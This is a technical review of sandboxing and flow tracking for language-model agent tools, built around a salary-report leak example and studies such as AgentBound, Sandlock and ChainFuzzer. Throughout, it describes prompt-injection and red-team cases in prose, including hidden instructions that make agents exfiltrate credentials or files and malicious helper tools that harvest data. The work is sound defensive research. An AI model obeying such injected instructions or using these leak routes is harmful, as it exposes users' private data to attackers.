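# Isolating and sandboxing the tools of language-model agents, and how data leaks between calls

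## How data passes between tool calls, and what isolation can mean

A language-model agent is a program that carries out a user's request by letting a large language model call tools. A tool is a function, such as one to read a file, search the web or send an email. A tool call is one request from the model to run that function with particular arguments. Tools give the agent access to private data and let it act on the outside world. Many come from third parties, and many bring in text that strangers wrote.

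Security engineers have long run software they do not fully trust in an isolated space where it can touch only what it needs. For agents, that means giving each tool or each app its own space and its own permissions. Most useful tasks, however, need data from one tool in a call to another, so the data has to leave one isolated space and enter the next. Isolation confines the tool, but it is less clear how much it controls data that leaves the tool by the permitted route. A rival family of defences, called flow tracking, labels the data itself and checks the labels before each call.

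### The agent loop

The model runs no tools itself. It produces a structured request, and an ordinary program around it does the work. Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the developer documentation for the company's Claude models, sets out the usual loop:

1. The application sends the model the user's request and a list of available tools, with a description of each tool and the format of its arguments.
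2. The model replies with a final answer or with one or more tool calls.
3. The application runs each call and collects the output.
4. The application sends the model a new request, which holds the original messages, the model's reply and the tool results.
5. Steps 2 to 4 repeat until the model stops asking for tools.

The model's context is the text it reads before each step. Because of step 4, the context keeps growing, and by the fifth call it contains the results of the first four in a single stream of text. Tools from different companies normally share that stream. Under the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common interface between agents and tool servers, each server publishes a list of its tool definitions, which applications add to the model's context.

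A tool, such as a mail tool, receives only the arguments that the model wrote for it, not the rest of the conversation. So even an agent with no defences keeps its tools somewhat isolated from each other, and their data comes together in the model.

Some tool-call loops run outside the application. Anthropic runs web search and code execution on its own servers, and several searches may finish before the application receives a response. A check in the application could then inspect those calls only after they have run.

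### The salary report

Jiang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *ChainCaps*, describe a small case that illustrates most of the problem. A user asks an agent for an executive summary. The agent reads a salary spreadsheet, fetches industry benchmarks from the web, summarises the two together and emails the result to a distribution list. It has permission for all four calls, but the email now contains salary data that was for internal use only. No tool malfunctioned and no attacker was involved. They call this permission laundering, where a restricted value passes through a series of permitted calls to a destination it should not reach.

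The spreadsheet and the web page are called sources, places where data enters the agent. The email is a sink, an action through which data leaves or has an effect. A permission check on the email tool can determine whether the agent may send mail, and perhaps to whom. But whether it may send this particular text depends on where the text came from, which the call does not record. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of the area, makes the general point that a valid permission at one boundary does not establish permission at the next, and that access to a document does not necessarily include authority to send it.

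Tighter rules on single tools do not fix this. If the company forbids the agent to send email, it loses the harmless reports along with the harmful one. Banning the sequence "read a file, then send mail" would also block harmless emails. For example, the agent could read the spreadsheet and then email a summary of only the public benchmarks, which is harmless if the model keeps other data out of the summary. Whether an email should be allowed depends on the data in it, which the list of calls does not show.

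The maintainers of MCP, drawing on practice, similarly argue in a post on tool annotations that risk depends on the whole session, because users routinely combine tools from several servers (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A tool that searches email is neither safe nor dangerous on its own. They borrow the programmer Simon Willison's phrase "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally, all of which the salary agent has.

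### Cross-call paths

A cross-call path is any route by which data or instructions from one tool call affect a later one. The simplest is copying, where the model writes something from a tool result into the arguments of the next call. The copy doesn't have to be word for word. A sentence like "our engineers earn about a tenth less than the market" reveals salary data without quoting any cell of the spreadsheet, so a filter that searches outgoing mail for known strings would miss it.

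A result can also steer the agent, changing which tool it calls next without supplying any of the text. In prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content that the model will read, say at the bottom of the benchmarks page, telling the agent to send the spreadsheet to another address. Zhou and Zhang imagine a workflow that asks some source whether a draft has approval for external release and accepts only "yes" or "no". That single bit can decide whether confidential data leaves the organisation. Restricting the reply to a fixed format limits what the source can express but doesn't reduce its influence over the decision.

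Tool descriptions enter the context before the agent calls anything, so a hostile tool can affect the plan without ever running. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (Sakib, Haque and colleagues, 2026) tested 13 models on the same tasks, with identical hostile text placed either in a tool's output or in its description. Gemini-3-Flash carried out the attacker's goal in 8.8% of cases when the text was in the output and 74.6% when it was in the description. For GPT-4.1, the rates were 54.9% for outputs and 6.8% for descriptions. But for the median model, testing outputs alone understated the worse of the two results by only 1.4 percentage points, and a few models account for most of the average understatement. Still, defences that repeated the user's instruction or marked untrusted text worked much better on outputs than on descriptions, so guarding only tool results leaves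 an agent fairly exposed to hostile descriptions.

Data can also pass between calls without going through the model's context. One call may write a file that a later call reads, perhaps in a different session the next day. Anthropic's standard tools include a memory store, a shell and a file editor, and each can hold data after the call that wrote it has ended. If the salary agent saves its summary to a shared folder, another task may attach the file to an email with no record of what went into it. Shared credentials also connect tools, because two tools with the same access token can act on the same account even if their code is isolated. A shell tool makes both problems worse, since it can usually reach the files and tokens of everything else on the machine. The Model Context Protocol maintainers cite a demonstration that chained a malicious calendar entry, a calendar server and a local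 code execution tool, and they consider the code execution tool the most important part of the chain.

The last path is through the user's approval. Many applications show a confirmation dialog before a risky call, and approving it can easily authorise a broader flow of data than the user meant. In Zhou and Zhang's example, a user agrees that the agent may send one summary to Alice. The system records this correctly but then issues a credential that grants general permission to send mail, so the mail service would also accept it for sending a different document to Bob. Applications also use tool annotations to decide when to ask for approval, and may skip the dialog for a tool marked as read-only. In MCP, that mark is only a hint. A server can falsely mark a tool as read-only and use it to delete files, which is why the maintainers want hard guarantees to come from sandboxes or network controls.

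### Threats and grains of isolation

How much each path matters depends on who, if anyone, is trying to use it. *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) gives three examples. In the first, the tool itself is malicious. A user with two ride-sharing apps asks for the cheaper fare, and one app could direct the model to inflate the other's price. In the second, hostile content arrives through an honest tool. The email app works as designed, but a message in the inbox contains instructions for the model to take documents from the user's cloud drive. The third, like the salary report, is a mistake with no attacker. The model misjudges what "personal data" should mean for each app and gives a travel app the personal data it had collected for a symptom-checking app.

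Models have become much harder to hijack through hostile content. The news site The Decoder reported that in a test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 5.5% of the time against Claude Opus 4.8 and 2.0% against Claude Opus 5. The test did not measure how often a model puts the wrong data in an email when nobody prompts it to, so the results are only indirectly relevant to the salary report.

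"Isolation" can refer to designs that put the boundary in quite different places. The finest-grained common design puts a sandbox around each tool process, as AgentBound does for MCP servers. A sandbox is a restricted environment, enforced by the operating system or a virtual machine, that limits which files, networks and system calls a program can use. In the salary example, the file reader might have access to one finance folder and no network, while the mail tool could reach the mail server but no files. That would stop a malicious mail tool from opening the spreadsheet itself, but it would not prevent the leak, because the model passes the figures from one tool to the other while both stay within their limits.

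A different design separates what the model reads. IsolateGPT gives each app its own model instance and memory, and a trusted hub passes messages between them. One ride-sharing app's description therefore never enters the context in which the model uses a competing app. In the salary report example, the outcome depends on which messages the hub passes. The user asked for an emailed summary, so the hub has to send one to the mail app, and a person or a program has to decide whether to allow it.

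Isolation can also separate trusted data from untrusted data. One agent holds the powerful tools and reads only trusted material, while another reads web pages and incoming mail and can do little by itself. PFI (Prompt Flow Integrity) is built on this split. It helps against hostile content, because instructions on the benchmarks page reach an agent that has no mail tool. But the salary spreadsheet is trusted, so a split based only on trust would leave it with the privileged agent, which also holds the mail tool.

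Papers that compare defences often use the broader term "per-function isolation" for any scheme that runs or authorises each tool function separately, with its own permissions and no direct access to other tools. This lets an operator write and check the rules for one function at a time, but rules checked this way can miss harm that comes from combining functions.

### Controlling access and controlling what follows

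The gap between these two kinds of control is much older than language models. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who runs someone else's program, the service, on private data. Engineers already knew how to stop the service from reading anything the customer had not granted. Lampson pointed out that the service could still pass on data the customer had deliberately given it, generally without the customer noticing. He called preventing this the confinement problem.

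Lampson's list of possible leaks still applies to modern agents. The service might keep the data until the service's owner next calls it, write the data to a file in the owner's directory, or send it in a message to the owner's process. It might encode a few bits in the bill. It might also vary its load on the machine so that another program could read the signal from the slowdown. This is an example of what Lampson called a covert channel, one not intended for communication at all.

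Lampson then looked for rules that would close these leaks. A confined program must be memoryless, keeping nothing within itself from one call to the next. Total isolation, in which the program also calls no other program, is enough, but he judged it "quite impractical". In its place he proposed a rule of transitivity, under which any program that a confined program calls must be either trusted or confined too. An agent fits neither requirement well, because its context is designed to keep data from call to call, and the mail tool cannot be confined when its purpose is to send data out. Trusting the mail tool to deliver messages faithfully does not help if the message itself contains data that should not leave.

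Dorothy Denning took the other approach in 1976 and attached the rule to the data. Most access control, Denning, in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, observed, governs immediate access to objects and ignores the paths along which information can then move. In her model every object has a security class. The relation A → B means that information in class A may flow into class B, and the operator ⊕ gives the class of a value computed from several others. If a program computes a value from objects a₁ to aₙ and stores it in b, then the flow is secure only if

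a₁ ⊕ a₂ ⊕ … ⊕ aₙ → b

where each letter now stands for the object's class. The salary report needs two classes, Public and Internal, with a flow from Public to Internal allowed and the reverse forbidden. The spreadsheet is Internal and the benchmarks page is Public, so a summary of both has the class Internal ⊕ Public, which is Internal. An email to outsiders is a Public object. Internal → Public does not hold, and the system refuses the call. A summary computed from the benchmarks alone has the class Public ⊕ Public = Public, and the same email may go. This is the distinction that permission checks on single calls could not draw.

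Under mild assumptions the classes form a lattice, in which any two classes have a least upper bound, the lowest class that both may flow into. The classes need not lie on one scale from open to secret. In one of Denning's examples they are sets drawn from medical, financial and criminal records, and a mixture of medical and financial data may enter only an object cleared for both. She also proposed controlling names, salaries and pairs of name and salary separately, since the pairs can be more sensitive than either list. For agents, the most important consequence of transitivity is that if every single operation is secure, so is any sequence of them. Per-tool permissions lack this property, which makes permission laundering possible.

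Denning distinguished explicit flows, in which a program copies or computes data into an object, from implicit ones. The statement "if a = 0 then b := 0" creates an implicit flow from a to b. If b starts at some other value, anyone who looks at it afterwards learns whether a was zero, even if the assignment never ran. Similarly, an agent would create an implicit flow by following an instruction to email a recruiter only if company pay is below the benchmark. A recruiter who knows about the instruction learns something even when no email arrives. The steering path contains many such flows, and they are harder to track than copies.

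Flow tracking, also called information-flow control, applies this idea to agents by attaching labels to data and checking them before each call. A label marks how secret or how trustworthy a piece of data is. Secrecy labels govern where data may go, which is the issue in the salary report. Trustworthiness is usually called integrity, and integrity labels govern what data may influence, which is the issue when a web page contains instructions for the mail tool. Data combined from several sources takes the most secret and the least trustworthy of their labels.

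In an ordinary program, an analyst can see which variables went into a result, but nobody can reliably say which parts of a language model's context shaped a given output. A cautious system therefore assumes that all of them did. Some of the mechanisms Denning reviewed worked this way, with a class for the whole process that only rose as it read more data. Once the spreadsheet is in an agent's context, even an email about a meeting time counts as Internal. Researchers call this spread of restrictions label creep. Practical systems need ways to relax labels. Declassification releases restricted data under some policy, and endorsement lets less trusted data influence a protected decision. Both are deliberate exceptions to the rule, and someone has to decide where to allow them. Denning concluded that a practical system needs both flow control and access control.

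### InjecAgent and AgentDojo

Much of the evidence on these defences comes from two 2024 benchmarks of prompt injection. *InjecAgent* (Zhan, Liang and colleagues, 2024) combines 17 user requests, each relying on a tool that returns outside content, with 62 attacker instructions to make 1,054 test cases. About half of the instructions aim at direct harm, such as unlocking a door or transferring money, and the rest aim at stealing data. Each test starts with the hostile tool result already in the context and measures what the agent does next, so the benchmark does not cover planning over a long task.

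GPT-4 in its standard prompted form followed the attacker's instructions in 24% of cases, and in 47% when the attack began with a line telling it to ignore previous instructions. Those rates come from models that are long out of date, but one result from the data-stealing cases remains more relevant. Each of these cases required two calls, one to fetch private data and one to send it out. GPT-4 made the first call in about a third of cases, and once it had, it made the second 97.7% of the time.

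Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built something closer to a working agent in *AgentDojo*. Its four simulated environments (an office workspace, Slack, travel booking and banking) keep real state such as inboxes, files and account balances, and a task can take up to 18 calls. The first version had 97 user tasks and paired each with every attacker goal in the same environment, for 629 security cases. Ordinary code inspects the environment afterwards to see whether the money moved or the email went out, so the benchmark doesn't rely on a second language model that the same injection might fool. The benchmark reports the share of tasks the agent completes with no attack, the share it completes correctly under attack, and the share of cases in which the attacker's goal comes about (the attack success rate). The first two scores would be very low for a defence that prevented every attack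 by blocking everything.

AgentDojo has since grown to more than 900 pairings, according to *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026), and *AgentDyn* (2026) extends the approach to open-ended tasks in which the agent has to replan as results come in. Every security case in InjecAgent and AgentDojo contains an attacker's instruction, so the attack success rate would not count an agent that leaked the salary figures by mistake. Scores against fixed attacks also tend to overstate how well a defence works. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) let an attacking model revise its injections after seeing which ones worked, and a filter that had blocked every fixed attack on GPT-4o-mini then let 28% of the revised attacks succeed.

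## Running each tool in its own operating-system sandbox

An agent on a personal computer usually starts a local MCP server as an ordinary process, with all the privileges of the user who launched it. A weather-forecast server can therefore read the user's SSH keys (files that log the user in to other machines), start other programs and contact any address on the internet. Running each server in a sandbox can limit it to what its job requires, but someone has to specify those permissions and the operating system has to enforce them. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that does both.

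### Manifests and containers in AgentBound

AgentBound follows the model of Android, where an app declares its permissions in advance. Each server comes with a manifest, a JSON file with a short English description of the server and a list of the capabilities it needs. The capabilities come from a fixed vocabulary that covers files, environment variables (settings that a program receives when it starts, often including passwords for online services), running other programs, network access, devices such as the camera, and a few extras such as the clipboard. To build this vocabulary, Bühler and colleagues mapped 16 uses of agents from the research literature to Android permissions and compared the result with the permission system on Apple's desktop computers. They then dropped the permissions that only make sense on a phone and added those that desktop servers need.

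A manifest entry is general, so it may list file reading without naming a folder. Before the server starts, the agent turns each capability into a concrete permission, such as read-only access to one project folder, and asks the user to approve it. If the agent asks for something outside the manifest, AgentBound aborts the run. Developers can write fixed permissions into the manifest, such as access to the only web address a weather server contacts. The user has to approve permissions that can change, such as access to the working folder, on every run.

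AgentBound then starts the server in its own Docker container, a group of processes with a separate view of the files and the network. Only the approved folders and environment variables exist inside it. The container first installs the server's software, then looks up the IP addresses of the permitted hosts and sets firewall rules that allow only those addresses. The server's code needs no changes.

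This design is coarser than it may sound. Each server has one container, so all the tools it offers run with the same permissions. For example, a mail server's search function has the same permissions as its send function. The firewall also filters only by address, so it can't allow one customer's account at an online service while blocking another's.

### What AgentBound stopped and what got through

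For their first security test, Bühler and colleagues wrote a server that tries to steal an SSH key. Without a sandbox, it read the key and sent it away. With the network blocked, it could read the key but not send it, and with the file rules in place, it couldn't read the key.

They then tried 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections, and the sandbox stopped nine of the attacks, including one combined attack that it only partly stopped. One of the nine was a Google Maps server whose code quietly replaces Google's address with another. The firewall allowed connections only to Google's address, so the connection failed. The sandbox doesn't have to recognise such code as malicious, because it blocks any attempt to open a forbidden file, whether the attempt comes from an attacker or a bug.

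Five attacks succeeded because they used only actions that the sandbox rules allowed. One exploited a flaw in how a server queried its own database, which the server needs to use. Another involved a server that tells the time. Its description contains an instruction to redirect cryptocurrency transfers to a "privacy proxy" whenever the model uses the wallet tool, which belongs to a different server. The time server stays within its permissions, and the wallet tool makes an ordinary transfer to the wrong recipient. The instruction reaches the model through its context, which neither container covers.

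One tester approved the permissions in these experiments, and ordinary users may be less careful. According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, users of the coding agent Claude Code approved roughly 93% of its permission prompts and paid less attention to each one the more prompts they saw. AgentBound requests approval when a server starts, so its users would see fewer prompts, but one careless approval would apply for the whole session.

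Few developers will write manifests by hand for thousands of existing servers, so Bühler and colleagues had language models draft them from the source code. GPT-5 mini wrote five drafts for each of 296 popular servers, and GPT-5 merged each set into one manifest. The researchers sent 96 of the merged manifests to the servers' developers and report an accuracy of 80.9%. But 74% of the developers never replied, and the published percentages imply that four more cases were under discussion. That leaves 21 manifests behind the accuracy figure, of which developers accepted 17 and rejected four.

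In a second, more informative check, two of the researchers wrote manifests by hand for 48 servers, and the generated manifests agreed with theirs on 96.5% of capabilities. This figure is also inflated, because it counts as agreement every capability that both versions left out, and most servers need only a few. The two versions matched exactly for 28 servers. Most of the errors were omissions, which would make a server fail but wouldn't expose anything.

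The drafts also give some idea of how much access a correct manifest grants. Of the 296 servers, 83.1% needed outgoing network access and 74.1% needed to read files, so at least 57% needed both. A malicious server with both permissions can read its permitted folder and send the contents to a permitted host without breaking any rule.

The delay from the sandbox is far shorter than the time a language model takes to produce a single reply. The sandbox usually added between 150 and 400 milliseconds when a server started, and less than a millisecond to each file or network operation after that.

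### A new sandbox for every call

AgentBound's containers last for a whole session, so a tool can carry data from one call to the next. Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues (2026), in *Signed, Sealed, Leaked*, built a document tool that does its advertised job but secretly keeps a copy of a salary sheet from an earlier call. When a later call sends an invoice to an outside text-recognition service, the tool adds the salary sheet to the request. The service is a permitted destination, so a firewall lets the request through. Meta's MCPGuard-Dynamic, another defence that limits files and destinations, missed the leak in every trial.

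Lampson's rule that a confined program must be memoryless applies to this case, and running each call in a new process comes close to enforcing it. Starting a container for every call would be slow, however, because an agent may run dozens of short commands a minute. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes a lighter sandbox built from features already in the Linux kernel. One of them, Landlock, lets a program without administrator rights give up access to files, network ports and some ways of communicating with other processes. Another, seccomp, filters system calls, which are the requests a program makes to the kernel, for example to open a file, connect to a network or start another program.

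Sandlock has its own policy format, so a host program (the agent application or the tool server) would have to translate an AgentBound manifest into it. With that step added, one call to the file reader in the salary example would run like this:

1. The host program looks up the file reader's manifest and the folder that the user approved. It writes a policy that allows reading from the salary folder and from the system libraries the tool needs, with no writing and no network.
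2. Sandlock creates a new process, which waits before it runs any of the tool's code.
3. The new process takes on the Landlock rules. From here on, the kernel refuses to open any file outside the listed folders.
4. The process then takes on a seccomp filter. The filter refuses some risky system calls that Landlock doesn't cover and sends a few others, such as certain network connections, to a supervisor outside the sandbox. All other calls go straight to the kernel.
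5. Once the supervisor is ready, the tool starts. It opens the spreadsheet, which the kernel allows. If it tried to open an SSH key instead, it would get an error.
6. The tool returns the spreadsheet's contents and the process ends, along with anything it held in memory. The host program passes the result to the model, where it joins the context.

A tool with network access needs more supervision. Sandlock looks up each permitted hostname once, at the start, and keeps that address, so an attacker can't redirect the name to another machine later. When the tool asks to connect to a host, the supervisor copies the requested address, checks the copy and uses it to make the connection, so another part of the tool can't swap the address after the check. An operator can also restrict web requests by type, host and path. For encrypted traffic, this works only if the tool accepts a security certificate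 from Sandlock, because the proxy that checks the requests has to read them.

Sandlock added about 5 milliseconds to a trivial command, and the same command took about 44 times as long in Docker. Sandlock refuses to run on Linux kernels older than 6.12, where it would have to enforce a weaker policy. Wang and Zheng ran ten simple checks, such as reading a file outside the granted folder or connecting to an unlisted host, and Sandlock allowed or denied each action as the policy required. None of the checks tried to break out of the sandbox. Wang and Zheng still recommend a small virtual machine with its own kernel for hostile customers who share one machine.

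Starting a new process for each call reduced leaks in tests by Aun and colleagues, who ran 153 attacks by tools with hidden malicious code. Protected data leaked in 51 runs when confinement like AgentBound's lasted the whole session, and in 15 when each call had a new process. Both setups also labeled what the tools returned. Aun and colleagues wrote the attacks themselves, so the results compare the designs but don't indicate how common such tools are. Restarting a tool can also take longer than starting the sandbox around it. Their Python tools took roughly 100 to 290 milliseconds per call when each call began with a new process.

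Most of the 15 remaining leaks did not depend on the tool keeping data between calls. In some, a single call gave the tool two documents, and the tool sent both to a destination that should have received only one. In others, one server left data where a second server could read it and send it on.

To close these routes, Aun and colleagues start a separate copy of the tool for each group of destinations and give it only the documents that those destinations may see. None of the 153 attacks leaked data under this scheme, and a call that needed one copy took 10 to 49 milliseconds. But someone has to label every document and decide which labels each destination may see, so the scheme is partly flow tracking. It also can't control what the model does with a result, so it passes the labels on to whatever system checks the model's next call.

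### One sandbox around the whole agent

Anthropic puts larger boundaries around its own agents, and they differ by product. In the chat service claude.ai, Claude runs code on Anthropic's servers, in a container that lasts only for the session. Claude Code runs on the developer's machine. Its sandbox lets commands read files, but they can write only inside the project folder and have no network access by default. The sandbox cut permission prompts by 84%. Claude Cowork, a product for office work, runs code in a full virtual machine with its own kernel. The virtual machine can access the folder the user selected and Claude's settings folder, but no other files, and the user's credentials stay outside it. Anthropic made this the strictest of the boundaries on a user's machine because typical office workers can't judge whether a shell command is safe.

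This kind of boundary protects the rest of the computer from the agent, whatever the reason for the harmful action. In an exercise in February 2026, one of Anthropic's security researchers tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt with harmful instructions hidden among routine ones. In 24 of 25 attempts, Claude read the employee's cloud credentials and sent them to an outside address. Safeguards designed to catch requests the user didn't make could not catch these instructions, because they came from the user. Limits on file and network access would have stopped the theft. AgentBound's containers might not have, because they isolate MCP servers, while Claude Code can run commands in its own shell.

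But all programs inside one large sandbox have the same access. A compromised program in Cowork's virtual machine can read or damage anything in the user's folder, including files from an unrelated task. Per-tool sandboxes also protect each tool's data from the other tools, provided each tool's permissions are narrow.

A large sandbox may also fail to cover the tools. Anthropic first ran local MCP servers inside Cowork's virtual machine but later moved them out, because they were hard to audit there, updates to the virtual machine broke them, and some had to communicate with databases and other programs on the host. Anthropic now treats them like any other software the user installs and leaves administrators to decide which ones to enable. The virtual machine no longer limits what those servers can do, so a sandbox like AgentBound's would add protection that Cowork's lacks.

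Open-source agents differ in the same way. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026) examined four of them in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*. IronClaw runs individual tools in a restricted environment, but only when it calls them directly rather than through an MCP server. NemoClaw runs the whole agent in a sandbox, which largely prevents a tool from bypassing its limits by calling an unconfined helper program. Companies that build their own agents may have to supply the sandbox themselves. *Beyond Training* (2026), a catalogue of controls for AI systems in operation, lists Anthropic's shell and file-editing tools among those that leave the sandbox to the customer, while OpenAI's toolkit for building agents includes one.

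Neither size of sandbox prevents leaks through a permitted destination. Cowork's network rules allowed access to Anthropic's own servers because Cowork cannot work without them. Outside researchers showed that a malicious file in the user's folder could contain hidden instructions and the attacker's own access key for Anthropic's service. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded the user's files to the attacker's account, and the network filter let the upload through because the address was approved. Anthropic now also checks whose key a request carries, and it advises others to treat each approved address as permission to use every function available there.

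A sandboxed program can also affect the host through files. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, covers cases in which the host runs something that a program inside the sandbox wrote.

### The salary report with a policy for each tool

Suppose the company in the salary example gives each of its three tools a separate sandbox, with about the tightest policy that still lets the tool do its job:

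| Tool | Files | Network | Secrets |
|---|---|---|---|
| File reader | Salary folder, read-only | None | None |
| Web fetcher | None | Benchmark site, download requests only | None |
| Mail tool | None | Company mail server only | Mail password |

Under these policies, the mail tool receives only what the model sends it. A compromised web fetcher can read neither the salaries nor the mail password. A compromised file reader can read the salaries but has no network connection to send them over. So an attacker who controls one of these tools can get the data out only through the model or through a flaw in the sandbox.

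The original leak still happens because the model runs outside the sandboxes and passes the summary to the mail tool as an argument. The salary data reaches everyone on the distribution list, but the logs of all three sandboxes would show no violations because no process has opened a forbidden file or contacted a forbidden host.

Tighter rules would help only a little. The kernel can detect that the mail tool has connected to the mail server, but the recipients' addresses and the text are sent inside that connection. A proxy that read each message could restrict the recipients, but it would have no record of where the text came from. Even without a mail tool, the model could leak a salary figure by putting it in the web address it asks the fetcher to download, unless the policy fixed the exact page.

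Sandlock can split a task into stages, so that the stage that reads private data has no network access and the stage with network access receives only what the first sends through a pipe. The kernel enforces this split, but Wang and Zheng state explicitly that Sandlock does not check the content of the pipe. In the salary report example, the summary has to go through that pipe. Pirch and colleagues found no comparable separation between tools' results in the four agents they examined, and suggest giving each call its own context with only the data it needs.

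A sandbox could block the leak if its policy changed after the agent read something sensitive. Adam, Lu and colleagues (2026) studied a similar case in *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*. A developer asks an agent to copy a settings file into a project and later to publish the project on GitHub. The file contains a secret key, so two permitted calls together make the key public. Adam and colleagues saw Claude Haiku 4.5 do this. When they replayed the recorded session with a single fixed sandbox around the tool server, the key still leaked. Preventing the leak would have required blocking all network access, which would also have stopped the agent from publishing harmless projects.

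Their own prototype gives each call a separate policy. After the agent has copied a file with a key in it, the sandbox for the publishing call either hides that file or has no network access. If the file contains nothing secret, publishing goes ahead. The prototype made the right decision in all three scenarios they tried, both when the agent did what the user wanted and when it did something harmful. But the developers of each tool have to build the sandbox into its code, and a program then checks that they did so correctly. So far it works only for tools written in Rust. *AgentKernel* (2026) describes the isolation in current sandbox products as mostly a matter of being inside or outside the sandbox, and similarly proposes computing each call's permissions partly from where its inputs came from.

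In Adam and colleagues' experiments, the sandbox received a suitable policy before each call, and the agent already knew whether the file contained a secret. A deployed system would have to work this out. For the salary report, it would have to identify the spreadsheet as the source of the figures in the summary.

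## How often tools in real agents can affect one another

The salary report leaks through tools that aren't malicious and make only permitted calls. Researchers have looked for similar weaknesses in existing agents and in the tools that developers install in them. Most of their tests add an attacker, who may control a tool, a web page or the user's own requests. Few of the tests ran each tool in its own sandbox, but we can usually tell from an attack's path whether separate sandboxes would have stopped it.

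### Malicious helper tools

Developers often give an agent a set of tools at once. The documentation of LangChain, a popular framework for building agents, recommends this so that the model can pick the most suitable tool and carry on if one is missing. In *Les Dissonances*, a paper for the NDSS security conference in February 2026, Li, Cui and colleagues studied what one malicious tool in such a set can do to the others. They call the attack cross-tool harvesting and polluting.

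The author of a malicious tool first has to get the agent to call it. They pick a popular tool and describe their own as a helper for it. LangChain's Yahoo Finance tool, for example, looks up news by stock ticker rather than by company name. Li and colleagues built a tool that converts names to tickers, and the agent called it just before the Yahoo tool, even though the model could have supplied the tickers itself. Other helpers checked the format of a tool's input, explained its error messages or validated its results. A helper can do the job in its description, so the sequence of calls looks sensible. It can also load that description from its author's server when the agent starts, so a reviewer who read the code beforehand may have seen only a harmless version.

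The framework doesn't let a helper read other tools' results directly. To harvest that data, the helper's author adds an argument for it and gives a plausible reason. In one experiment, a helper for an airport search requested the user's current address, supposedly to check the location, and the model supplied it from the context. A helper can also pollute another tool's data by changing the tool's input, if the helper runs first, or its result, if the helper runs afterwards. In one test, a lookup of Netflix's share price was changed to a lookup of Nike's.

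Li and colleagues wrote a program called Chord to see how many real tools this works on. It takes an existing tool, has GPT-4o write malicious helpers for it, and gives an agent tasks that need the tool. Chord tried each attack five times with different requests and counted the tool as vulnerable if any attempt succeeded. The researchers collected 281 tools from LangChain and a second framework, LlamaIndex, but tested only the 66 they could set up fairly easily and without a paid account.

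| Result, out of 66 tools | Helper runs before the tool | Helper runs after the tool | Either |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent calls the helper | 47 | 35 | 50 |
| Helper collects data | 45 | 31 | 48 |
| Helper corrupts data | 35 | 25 | 45 |

A tool counted as vulnerable if even one of five attempts succeeded, but many tools were attacked successfully far more often. Among the LangChain tools where the attack worked at all, the median success rate for getting the agent to call a helper first was 100%. Corrupting data was less reliable, succeeding in two or more of the five attempts for only half of the tools vulnerable to it.

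The harvested data included document contents and physical addresses, but also non-sensitive items such as search topics and the names of public companies. A helper that runs before a tool can't collect that tool's results, because they don't exist yet. The 31 tools in the middle column are therefore the better guide to how often one tool's output could reach another.

The same helpers worked less often on two weaker models. Agents called a helper first in 75% of cases with GPT-4o, 58% with GPT-OSS 120B and 26% with Llama 4 Scout. Li and colleagues think stronger models are more susceptible because they better understand how a helper relates to the other tool. But Chord wrote and tuned these helpers with GPT-4o, which could explain part of the difference. All three models are also now old.

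Four existing defences made little difference in a test on ten of the tools. Without any defence, the agent called a helper first in 78% of attempts. Marking tool outputs as untrusted worked best, reducing this to 60%. Another defence removed tools that the task didn't seem to need, but it sometimes removed the useful tool along with the helper. Defences that scan results for suspicious instructions had nothing to find, because the helpers return only plausible data. Malicious descriptions also got helpers past the planners in IsolateGPT and ACE, another design that isolates whole apps.

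All of these attacks go through the model's context, which sandboxes around the tools don't cover. A sandbox could still stop a helper from sending the harvested data to its author if the manifest allowed no network access, which would be a reasonable rule for a tool that only checks formatting. But a tool that looks up tickers has a plausible reason to contact its own server, and most users would probably approve that access. A helper can also corrupt data without a network connection by returning a wrong number.

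### Chains that end in a risky operation

Tools that aren't malicious can also do harm if one of them fetches an attacker's text and another runs it. *ChainFuzzer* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to find a patch for a bug. The agent searches the web, downloads a file, saves it and runs it. Each step makes sense for the task, but the file may contain malicious code.

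ChainFuzzer is a program that looks for such chains in an agent's source code and then tries them out:

1. It searches each tool's code for risky operations, such as running a command or querying a database, and keeps the tools whose inputs can reach one. These tools are the sinks.
2. From each sink, it works backwards to the tools that could supply its input. Sometimes one tool's output fits another's input directly. In other cases, one tool stores something in a file or database and another reads it later. A language model then discards chains that no realistic task would use.
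3. It writes a request that leads the agent through the chain, and revises the request until the agent completes the chain five times in a row.
4. It adds a harmful test input, either to the user's request or to outside content such as a web page. If the model refuses, ChainFuzzer disguises the input and tries again.
5. It checks what happened at the sink. For a network request, the test is whether the request went to an internal address that the attacker chose. For a command, it is enough that the attacker's text reached the function that runs commands.

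Wu and colleagues ran ChainFuzzer on 20 open-source agents and frameworks, each with at least 2,000 GitHub stars. All 20 used GPT-5.1, and together they had 998 tools. ChainFuzzer confirmed 365 vulnerabilities in 19 of the 20, and 302 of these needed more than one tool.

The researchers did not compare results with and without sandboxes, but they note that sandbox permissions and blocked network access can stop a chain from working. The last column of this table gives the likely effect, based on how per-tool sandboxes work.

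| What the attacker controls | Vulnerabilities | Of these, through outside content | Likely effect of a sandbox around each tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| A command | 121 | 39 | The command runs, but only with the tool's own permissions |
| The address of a network request | 97 | 53 | The request fails unless the policy permits that address |
| Program code | 79 | 26 | The code runs, but only with the tool's own permissions |
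| A database query | 45 | 16 | None, if the tool needs that database |
| A text template that can contain code | 23 | 6 | The code runs, but only with the tool's own permissions |

In the bug-fix example, the damage would depend on the permissions of the tool that runs the patch. If that tool can read the project and contact a code-hosting site, a malicious patch could upload the project there. A stricter policy could stop the attack earlier by denying the tool access to the download folder, but then the agent couldn't apply legitimate patches either.

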